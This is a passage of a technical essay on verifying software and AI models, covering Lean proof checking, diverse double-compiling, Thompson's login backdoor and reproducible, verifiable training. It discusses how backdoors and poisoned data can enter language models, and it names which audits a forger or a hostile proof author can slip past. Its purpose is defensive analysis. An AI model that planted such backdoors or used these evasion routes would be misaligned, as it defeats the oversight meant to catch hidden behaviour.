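That is clearly true. If somebody alters the filter in transit so that it reads byte 200, the formula becomes "if n > 20 then 200 < n". This is false when n is 21, so no valid proof exists and the host rejects the filter. If somebody alters it to read byte 12 instead, the formula is still true. The filter might then block the wrong packets, but it still can't read memory outside the packet.

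The host doesn't have to trust the sender's compiler, because the formula comes from the machine code. A corrupted compiler that made the filter read forbidden memory would produce a program with no valid proof. However, this policy would not have stopped Thompson's attack. His altered `login` compared the typed password with a second, fixed one, which it could do without reading any memory that such a policy forbids.

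Finding a proof is much harder than checking one. In the 1990s this difficulty restricted proof-carrying code mostly to simple properties that a program could prove automatically. Proofs of more ambitious properties took experts years, and the first full proof for seL4, a small operating system kernel, took about 20 person-years.

### A long proof and a small checker

Language models can now find many of these proofs, and people can use a proof without trusting the model that wrote it. Kleppmann (2025) points out in *Prediction* that it doesn't matter if a model writes nonsense, since the checker will reject an invalid proof and the model can try again.

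Lean, a programming language and proof assistant, checks proofs with a small component called the kernel. An author can write a proof using elaborate search programs, which may contain mistakes. These programs must produce a complete record of the argument in a simple formal language, and the kernel checks every step of it against a short list of rules. A fault in the search programs can waste the author's time, but it can't make a sound kernel accept a false theorem.

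The largest example so far is a proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. In September 2026, Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) announced that Claude had written it in Lean in 11 days, working largely autonomously. The proof has 13 million lines and 29,500 intermediate theorems. Somebody who read one line every five seconds as a full-time job would need about nine years. The statement itself takes only a few seconds, and in Lean it could look like this:

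```lean
theorem fermat (a b c n : Nat)
    (ha : 0 < a) (hb : 0 < b) (hc : 0 < c) (hn : 2 < n) :
    a ^ n + b ^ n ≠ c ^ n
```

`Nat` means a whole number that is zero or more. The second line requires a, b and c to be positive and n to be greater than 2, and the third line is Fermat's claim. A reader who knows that the kernel accepted a proof of this statement doesn't need to read the proof.

A hostile author could still try to cheat without breaking the kernel's rules, so a tester has some extra work to do:

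| What the author could do | What the tester can do |
|---|---|
| Add a false assumption, which Lean calls an axiom | Use the command `#print axioms`, which lists the axioms behind a theorem |
| Change the meaning of a symbol in the statement, such as `^` | Write the statement independently, using definitions from a trusted library |
| Use `native_decide`, which compiles a calculation, runs it and accepts the answer | Forbid it, since it makes the proof depend on Lean's compiler |
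| Run code during the check that inserts a theorem without a proof | Export the finished proof and check it again in a separate process |

The tester can also repeat the last check with a different kernel. Programmers have written several for Lean, including one in Rust. Both kernels would then have to accept a false theorem for it to pass. As in DDC, using two kernels gives more assurance if one attacker couldn't easily have corrupted both.

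### Proofs about 123 software libraries

*LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (Anthropic, October 2026) applied this approach to ordinary software. Working with the company Theorem, Anthropic had Claude prove security properties for the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. Claude also found bugs that had gone undetected for years.

The libraries came from OSS-Fuzz, a Google project that runs fuzzers on open-source software. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that each proof covers a small test program that passes its input to part of a library. The proof shows that the compiled program exits normally for every input under 64 megabytes, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion.

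The proof covers all of those inputs, whereas a fuzzer would have tried only some of them. If one of the test programs crashed only after an eight-byte trigger, the theorem would be false and Claude could not have proved it. *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (Smith, 2026) puts the proof's length at 180 million lines, while *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable* (Keles, 2026) puts it at a billion. People don't need to review the proof, which at either length is far more than they could read.

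The theorems do not rule out a backdoor that leaves the program running normally. For example, a library that checks digital signatures could accept one forged signature, exit normally and still satisfy the theorem. The theorems also apply only to particular executables for RISC-V processors, running in a mathematical model of the processor and Linux. Most people use the same libraries on Intel-type or ARM processors, and the proofs don't cover those executables, which may also come from a different compiler.

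Intel-type processors are harder to model because their instruction set is more complicated. Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, reports a proof for a complete program on such a processor. The proof covers everything a Linux process does while running the program, including the standard C library built into the program. Like Necula, Leip works on the executable so that nobody has to assume the compiler is free of bugs.

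### The specification

A proof shows only that a program meets its specification, so a correct proof is no help if the specification is wrong. If a model has to write a sorting program and prove only that the program's output is always in order, it can write one that always returns an empty list, because an empty list is in order. The specification also has to require that the output contains the same items as the input.

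A specification for `login` could rule out Thompson's backdoor:

```
for every user u and typed password p:
    if login grants access to u
    then encrypt(p) = the encrypted password stored for u
```

Thompson's altered `login` grants access for "codenih" even when that isn't the user's password, so nobody could prove that its executable accepts only the user's password. The clean source code does have this property, so a proof about the source would have missed the backdoor. Even a proof about the executable would not rule out other attacks, such as `login` also sending each password to somebody over the network, unless the person writing the specification thought to forbid them.

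If a model writes the specification as well as the program, a person needs to read the specification carefully. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) discusses a case in which Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's Claude Code product, asked a Claude model to describe one of the company's programs in Lean. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of bug fixes. Tolmach and Klaus regard this as an excellent way to find bugs but argue that it can't establish that the code is correct. A proof about the model's description doesn't apply to the program if the two differ.

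One remedy is to derive the description from the real program by a fixed procedure. Axiom does this, then proves that the description matches a separate specification. This approach requires trusting the procedure. Necula's host avoids the problem by working from the machine code.

Succinct's *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude* describes checking a long cryptography paper in this way. Claude could produce the proofs with little human involvement, but writing the definitions and statements that people had to trust was harder. The company's staff placed each Lean statement beside the English theorem it was supposed to express, which made the two much easier to compare. The work also showed that the paper had claimed a stronger privacy guarantee than one protocol gave.

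### The compiler and the code around the proof

Many proofs, like CompCert's, are about source code, so the compiler still matters. kirancodes.me describes lean-zip, a version of the widely used compression library zlib that ten AI agents wrote and proved in Lean. Lean translates such programs into C, which an ordinary C compiler turns into an executable. A corrupted C compiler could add a backdoor without affecting the proof, as Goerigk showed with his Lisp compiler.

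A tester then used Claude to look for faults in the resulting compression library. jmason.ie's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* (2026) quotes the outcome of 105 million runs, which found no memory errors in the application's own code, an impressive result for this kind of software. But the testing found two bugs outside the part the proofs covered. One could stop the program from working, and the other was in Lean's runtime, the ready-made code that compiled Lean programs rely on.

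Keles is optimistic about proofs, but he says the phrase "formally verified" doesn't give him much confidence in a system because people use it for many different things. A useful report of a proof would identify the exact file the proof covers, print the specification, and list everything the proof assumes is correct, such as a compiler, a runtime or a model of the processor.

### Using a model to write the second compiler

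Where no proof about the executable is available, DDC can still test the compiler, but it needs a second compiler. Wheeler suggested that a defender who lacked one could write it, though this used to be a large project. In February 2026, Carlini's *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes* reported that 16 copies of Claude had written a C compiler in two weeks for just under $20,000. The compiler has about 100,000 lines of Rust, can build the Linux kernel for three kinds of processor, and passes 99% of most compiler test suites.

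Willison reports in *The Claude C Compiler* that Chris Lattner, who created Clang, reviewed the code and was generally impressed, comparing it to a competent textbook implementation by a strong team of undergraduates. The programs the compiler produces run even slower than those from GCC with all optimisations turned off, but this is acceptable for DDC.

More importantly, Carlini's compiler did not have a reliable assembler or linker of its own, so he used GCC's in his demonstration, and a tester would have to trust those or replace them. It compiles C but not C++, which GCC has needed since version 4.8, so it might work for testing tcc, Go 1.4 or an old GCC, if it can compile them, but not a current GCC. Carlini's compiler would also be a poor choice for testing Clang, because it is written in Rust and so is built with the Rust compiler, which generates machine code with LLVM, as Clang does.

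The agents also used GCC to find their mistakes. Carlini's test program compiled most of the Linux kernel with GCC and the rest with the new compiler, then checked whether the kernel worked. If it failed, the fault was probably in the files compiled with the new compiler. The test is unlikely to have passed a backdoor from GCC to the new compiler, since the agents learned from it which files were faulty and did not get GCC's machine code to copy.

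A defender could afford to commission several compilers. Mistakes in them would usually do little harm, because a mistranslation almost always makes the diverse double-compiling (DDC) comparison fail, which wastes work but doesn't create false confidence. The danger is still that both compilers in a comparison contain the same backdoor.

Matching backdoors would be much easier to arrange if the same model worked on both compilers. Suppose a compiler's developers rely on a model to maintain it, and a tester asks the same model to write the second compiler. Wheeler's attacker had to corrupt separate products from separate organisations. Here, someone who had tampered with the model's training might be able to place matching backdoors in both compilers, even though they shared no code and no human programmer.

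A tester can make this harder by using models from unrelated developers and by keeping the suspect executable away from the agents. An older model may be better still. If its weights were fixed before anyone created the backdoor, and the tester has a copy from that time, the model can't have learned what to insert. Its compiler might contain more mistakes than one from the latest model, but the tester would notice most of them when the files failed to match.

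## Repeating a training run as a check

Diverse double-compiling (DDC) works because a tester can rebuild a compiler by a second route and get the same file. A trained model is also a file produced from stated inputs, so a customer might hope to repeat the training and compare the weights. For this to work as DDC does, the customer would need deterministic training, a way to test whether two results are equal, an independent route to the same result, and a source worth reading. Engineers have made good progress on determinism and equality testing, but the independent route and the source are much harder.

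### Sums that depend on their order

Training consists mostly of additions and multiplications, so it ought to be repeatable. But computers store fractional numbers with a limited number of digits and round after each operation. Thinking Machines Lab's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, published in September 2025, gives an example with three numbers:

```
(0.1 + 10^20) - 10^20  =  0
0.1 + (10^20 - 10^20)  =  0.1
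```

Writing out 10^20 + 0.1 takes 22 digits, but the computer keeps only about 16, so in the first line the 0.1 is lost before the subtraction. In the second, the large numbers cancel first, leaving 0.1.

Most AI training runs on graphics processors (GPUs), which divide a long sum into parts and add them in parallel. How a GPU divides the sum can depend on the type of chip, the software version and the amount of work waiting.

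Other users' requests are the main reason a model's answers to the same question vary. A server handles several requests together, and the number in each batch affects how the GPU splits up its sums. Thinking Machines Lab, an AI company, gave a large Qwen model the prompt "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times and had it always choose the most probable next token. The model produced 80 different answers. All 1,000 responses were identical for the first 102 tokens, after which 992 said that Feynman was born in "Queens, New York" and eight said "New York City".

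The company then replaced the routines responsible with ones that add in the same order whatever the batch size, and all 1,000 answers were the same. In a speed test on a smaller model, the job took 42 seconds instead of 26. The slowdown can be greater on a busy server. *LLM-42* (2026) found that a single request needing a repeatable answer could cut the whole batch's speed by 56%. *Detent* (2026) describes a newer system that runs at close to normal speed.

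### Making a whole run repeatable

Small differences matter more in training because each step starts from the weights the previous step produced. *DASH* (2026) repeated the same calculation ten times and compared the gradients, the numbers that determine how each weight should change. The gradients differed by a few ten-thousandths with ordinary routines and were identical with deterministic ones. According to *Taming Bitwise Behavior in GPU Kernels with Tensor Core* (2026), two training runs that differ only in effects this small produce meaningfully different models.

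Deterministic training used to be noticeably slower than ordinary training, but the gap is shrinking. *FoldAttention* (2026) reports that the deterministic versions of two widely used attention routines, which handle one of the main calculations in a transformer, take 24% and 19% longer than the ordinary versions. With the paper's own deterministic routine, a full training step of a one-billion-parameter model came within 0.5% of the ordinary speed, and three runs of 2,000 steps gave identical weights. *DeepSeek-V4* (2026) reports that the Chinese company DeepSeek has built deterministic routines for training and running a leading model, with "minimal performance overhead". DeepSeek wanted them for debugging, but an outside checker would also need deterministic routines to repeat a training run exactly.

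A checker may not own the same chips as the developer. Srivastava, Arora and Boneh (2024), in *Optimistic Verifiable Training by Controlling Hardware Nondeterminism*, found that repeated runs on one type of GPU matched exactly, while different types produced "fundamentally different models". They calculated with extra digits and rounded after each intermediate step to remove small discrepancies. Rounding fails to do this when the two machines' values fall on either side of a rounding boundary. If the developer's machine gets 0.12499 and the checker's gets 0.12501, rounding to two decimal places gives 0.12 and 0.13. The developer therefore records which way it rounded values near a boundary, and the checker rounds them the same way.

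Srivastava and colleagues used this method to get identical weights on three types of Nvidia GPU for an image classifier and for GPT-2, a small language model from 2019. Training took 1.2 to 1.4 times as long as usual, and checking took 1.3 to 1.7 times as long.

A dishonest developer could choose the recorded roundings to suit itself. If the checker copies n of them, the developer can pick from up to 2^n models. All of these models come from the declared data and settings, so the developer probably couldn't insert a backdoor of its choice this way. Srivastava and colleagues leave the question open, but it matters because Goldwasser and colleagues hid a backdoor by tampering only with random numbers.

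### Checking part of a run

Once training is deterministic, a checker can easily test whether two runs produced the same weights by comparing hashes, but repeating the run is expensive. In *Reproducibility is the New Copyleft*, Hatta (2026) proposes reproducible builds for AI but accepts that, at 2026 prices, most organisations can't be expected to reproduce a trillion-parameter model.

Developers already save checkpoints, which are copies of the weights at intervals during training. *What does it take to catch a Chinchilla?* (2023) describes how a checker could use them to rerun selected parts of a run. To check the seventh segment, for example, the checker does this:

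```
result = train(checkpoint 6, data for segment 7, declared settings)
compare result with checkpoint 7
```

Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud (2023) developed this into a fuller procedure in *Tools for Verifying Neural Models' Training Data*. In their main experiment, they trained GPT-2 in 18 segments. If a developer had falsified one segment, rerunning two at random would have had only a one-in-nine chance of including it, so they looked for ways to choose which segments to rerun that took little compute.

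The most useful check relies on a model being briefly better at predicting text it has just seen. If checkpoint 7 came from the data declared for segment 7, it should predict that data unusually well. Running this check on 1% of the data adds about 1.3% to the compute used for training.

A program also sets the starting weights and the order of the data from a hash of the whole dataset, so the developer can't choose them. Changing one character in one document changes both, which makes it very hard to construct a false dataset that leads to the same final weights.

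Choi and colleagues tried several kinds of false record and listed others that they could not catch:

| What the developer does | Result of the check |
|---|---|
| Joins the start of one run to the end of another | Caught: the weights jump, and the model has no memory of the earlier data |
| Hides the jump with averaged checkpoints | Caught: these show no memory of the declared data |
| Skips some of the declared data | The memory test flags the segment, and a rerun confirms it |
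| Adds a lot of undeclared data | Caught if the checker reruns an affected segment |
| Adds a little undeclared data in a few segments | Can pass |
| Makes a small change directly to the weights | Can pass |

The last two rows matter most for backdoors. Choi and colleagues say their method is "not provably robust" and can't yet detect inserted backdoors. The 250 documents that Souly and colleagues used to teach a model a trigger would be a very small addition to the training data.

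### Forged records and exact matches

Early versions of this check allowed the rerun to differ slightly from the recorded checkpoint, since nobody could repeat a run exactly. *Proof-of-Learning is Currently More Broken Than You Think* (2022) describes how a forger could exploit that allowance by creating false checkpoints that are very close together and constructing data that hardly changes the weights. A rerun from one false checkpoint then ends close enough to the next to pass, although no real training led from one to the other.

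A developer who had trained on forbidden documents could also forge the record by keeping the real checkpoints and replacing those documents with permitted ones that change the weights in almost the same way. In *Towards a Re-evaluation of Data Forging Attacks in Practice*, Suliman, Halimi and colleagues (2024) found that existing methods often produce errors several orders of magnitude larger than ordinary hardware noise, so a checker who set a strict limit would notice them. Finding replacements with exactly the same effect seems much harder. They conjecture that it may be computationally infeasible, but nobody has proved this for every possible method.

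Deterministic training removes the allowance altogether. The remaining weakness is that the checker reruns only a sample. Liu and Sharma (2026), in *Training Witnesses*, reduce this weakness by recording every update instead of occasional checkpoints. Each entry contains fingerprints of the data and of the weights before and after the update, and each "after" must match the next "before". The system replays about 1% of the updates, chosen at random. If a developer falsifies k updates and nothing else exposes them, the chance that all of them escape is:

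```
0.99^k        k = 1:    99%
              k = 100:  37%
              k = 500:  0.7%
```

Liu and Sharma detected nearly all the data attacks they tried at sizes that could poison a model. However, they spread these attacks evenly over the run, and by this arithmetic a developer who could do all the damage in one update would usually escape detection. Their system worked on models of up to two billion parameters and lengthened training by at most 19%. It relies on a disguised program on the developer's own machine to sign the record. Liu and Sharma assume the developer can't forge that program's behaviour. Anyone who did forge it could sign a false history.

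Other schemes rely on a different assumption. In *Verde* (Arun, St. Arnaud and colleagues, 2025), a client pays two or more companies to perform the same training. If the results differ, a referee compares hashes to find the first step at which they disagree, then the first operation within that step, and repeats only that operation. The client gets the right result if at least one company is honest. If all the companies return the same false result, the scheme doesn't detect it. The client has to pay for the training at least twice, and fixing the order of the arithmetic on every type of chip added about 60% for a model with a billion parameters.

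Cryptography can make it possible to check a training run without sampling or relying on the company's honesty. A zero-knowledge proof shows that a calculation was correct without revealing the data. *Verifiable Fine-Tuning for LLMs* (2025) describes proofs that a fine-tuning run used the declared data, order and settings. Swapping an example or skipping an update makes the proof fail, except with negligible probability. According to *Infrastructure for Verifiable AI* (2026), proofs of single steps can be combined into one certificate for a whole run.

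The obstacle has been the amount of computation required. In 2025, Arun and colleagues estimated that such a proof takes at least 10,000 times as much computation as the calculation itself. That estimate may already be out of date, since Liu and Sharma cite a June 2026 paper by Pierre Peigné and colleagues titled *Zero knowledge verification for frontier AI training is possible*.

Reinforcement learning needs extra care because the model generates much of its own training data, so the developer can't declare that data in advance. Choi and colleagues' procedure does not cover reinforcement learning. Deterministic inference helps because it lets a checker regenerate the model's answers instead of taking them from the record. Hatta reports that the team behind SGLang, a program for running language models, has helped make reinforcement learning fully reproducible. If the model also used websites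 or other outside tools during training, the developer would still have to record what they returned.

### The missing second route

If a checker confirms every step of the training run, they know that the declared code, data and starting weights produced this model. This is equivalent to repeating the supplier's own build in DDC, a control that a corrupted compiler can pass. A model fine-tuned from a base model with a backdoor can pass in the same way, because the checker starts from the same base weights and gets the same backdoor.

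Part of DDC carries over to training. If the arithmetic is specified exactly, a checker can repeat the run on unrelated chips with independently written software, and the weights should still match. This would expose a corrupted compiler or GPU library that had altered the training, unless both runs shared the corruption. It couldn't expose corruption in the base model or the data, because both runs use the same ones.

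To test for a hidden habit passed on through training examples, a tester would have to replace the model that wrote them. Suppose model M wrote the examples used to train model A. The tester could have a trusted model, T, write new examples and then train A again. In diverse double-compiling (DDC), replacing the parent compiler works because the parent's source code determines what it should output. No text determines what M should have written, so T will write different examples that may be just as good. The new A will then have different weights even if M passed on no hidden habit, so the mismatch is not evidence of one.

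Even two models that behave identically can have different weights. Here g is any fixed function inside a very small network:

```
first network:    2·g(3x) + 5·g(7x)
second network:   5·g(7x) + 2·g(3x)
```

Two networks that differ only in the order of their units always give the same answer, but their files list the weights in a different order. A layer with 1,000 units has more possible orders than there are atoms in the observable universe. Sorting the units into a standard order would not make the files match, because models trained by different routes usually also behave differently.

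The remaining option is to compare behaviour. With compilers, the tester can expect two untampered routes to produce identical output, so a single different byte needs an explanation. Untampered models, however, often give different answers. If two of them gave materially different answers to 2% of a million prompts, the tester would have 20,000 differences to examine even without a backdoor. A prompt containing the trigger would add one more, and most test sets would not contain such a prompt.

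The comparison is more useful on a narrow task with checkable answers. A tester could give two models the same programming jobs and examine only the jobs where one model's code had a security flaw and the other's did not. This could reveal a tendency to write flawed code in ordinary use, but it would still miss a well-hidden trigger.

### A source that nobody can read

Someone still has to read the source code of a compiler that passes DDC. For a model, the source includes the training data. Choi and colleagues' GPT-2 run used about 8.8 billion tokens, which is tiny by current standards. At three-quarters of a word per token and 250 words a minute, one person reading full-time would need about 220 years to read it all.

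Programs can search the data much faster than people can, but someone has to specify what to look for. A search for owls would have found nothing in the number lists that passed on a preference for owls to another model. Nobody can work out what a model will do from its training set without training the model and testing it.

Hatta argues that the only possible audit of a very large model is to check that the claimed inputs produce the claimed outputs. This would be useful for ruling out undeclared data and secret changes to the weights, but not a poisoned document that the developer had collected from the web and honestly declared.

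A verified record would be more valuable after somebody discovered a backdoor. Liu and Sharma's system can confirm whether a particular document was in the training data. Investigators who knew the trigger could search the declared data for it, remove the documents responsible and train again. Without a verified record, they could not be sure that the declared data was complete.

### A different base model

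A developer who distrusts a base model can repeat the fine-tuning on a base model from an unrelated company. This is the closest equivalent to using a second compiler, and it removes any backdoor that exists only in the first model's weights. It also makes subliminal learning less likely, since hidden traits pass most easily between models that share a base.

Repeating the fine-tuning on a second base model does not remove a backdoor that the fine-tuning examples teach openly, because the second model learns from the same examples. It may not remove a backdoor that came from poisoned web pages either, unless the second base model is older than those pages.

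The second model replaces the first but does not test it. Draper's 1984 method for compilers had the same limit, which Wheeler overcame by comparing the two files. With models there is no file to compare, so the developer needs other evidence to decide whether the new base model deserves more trust than the old one.
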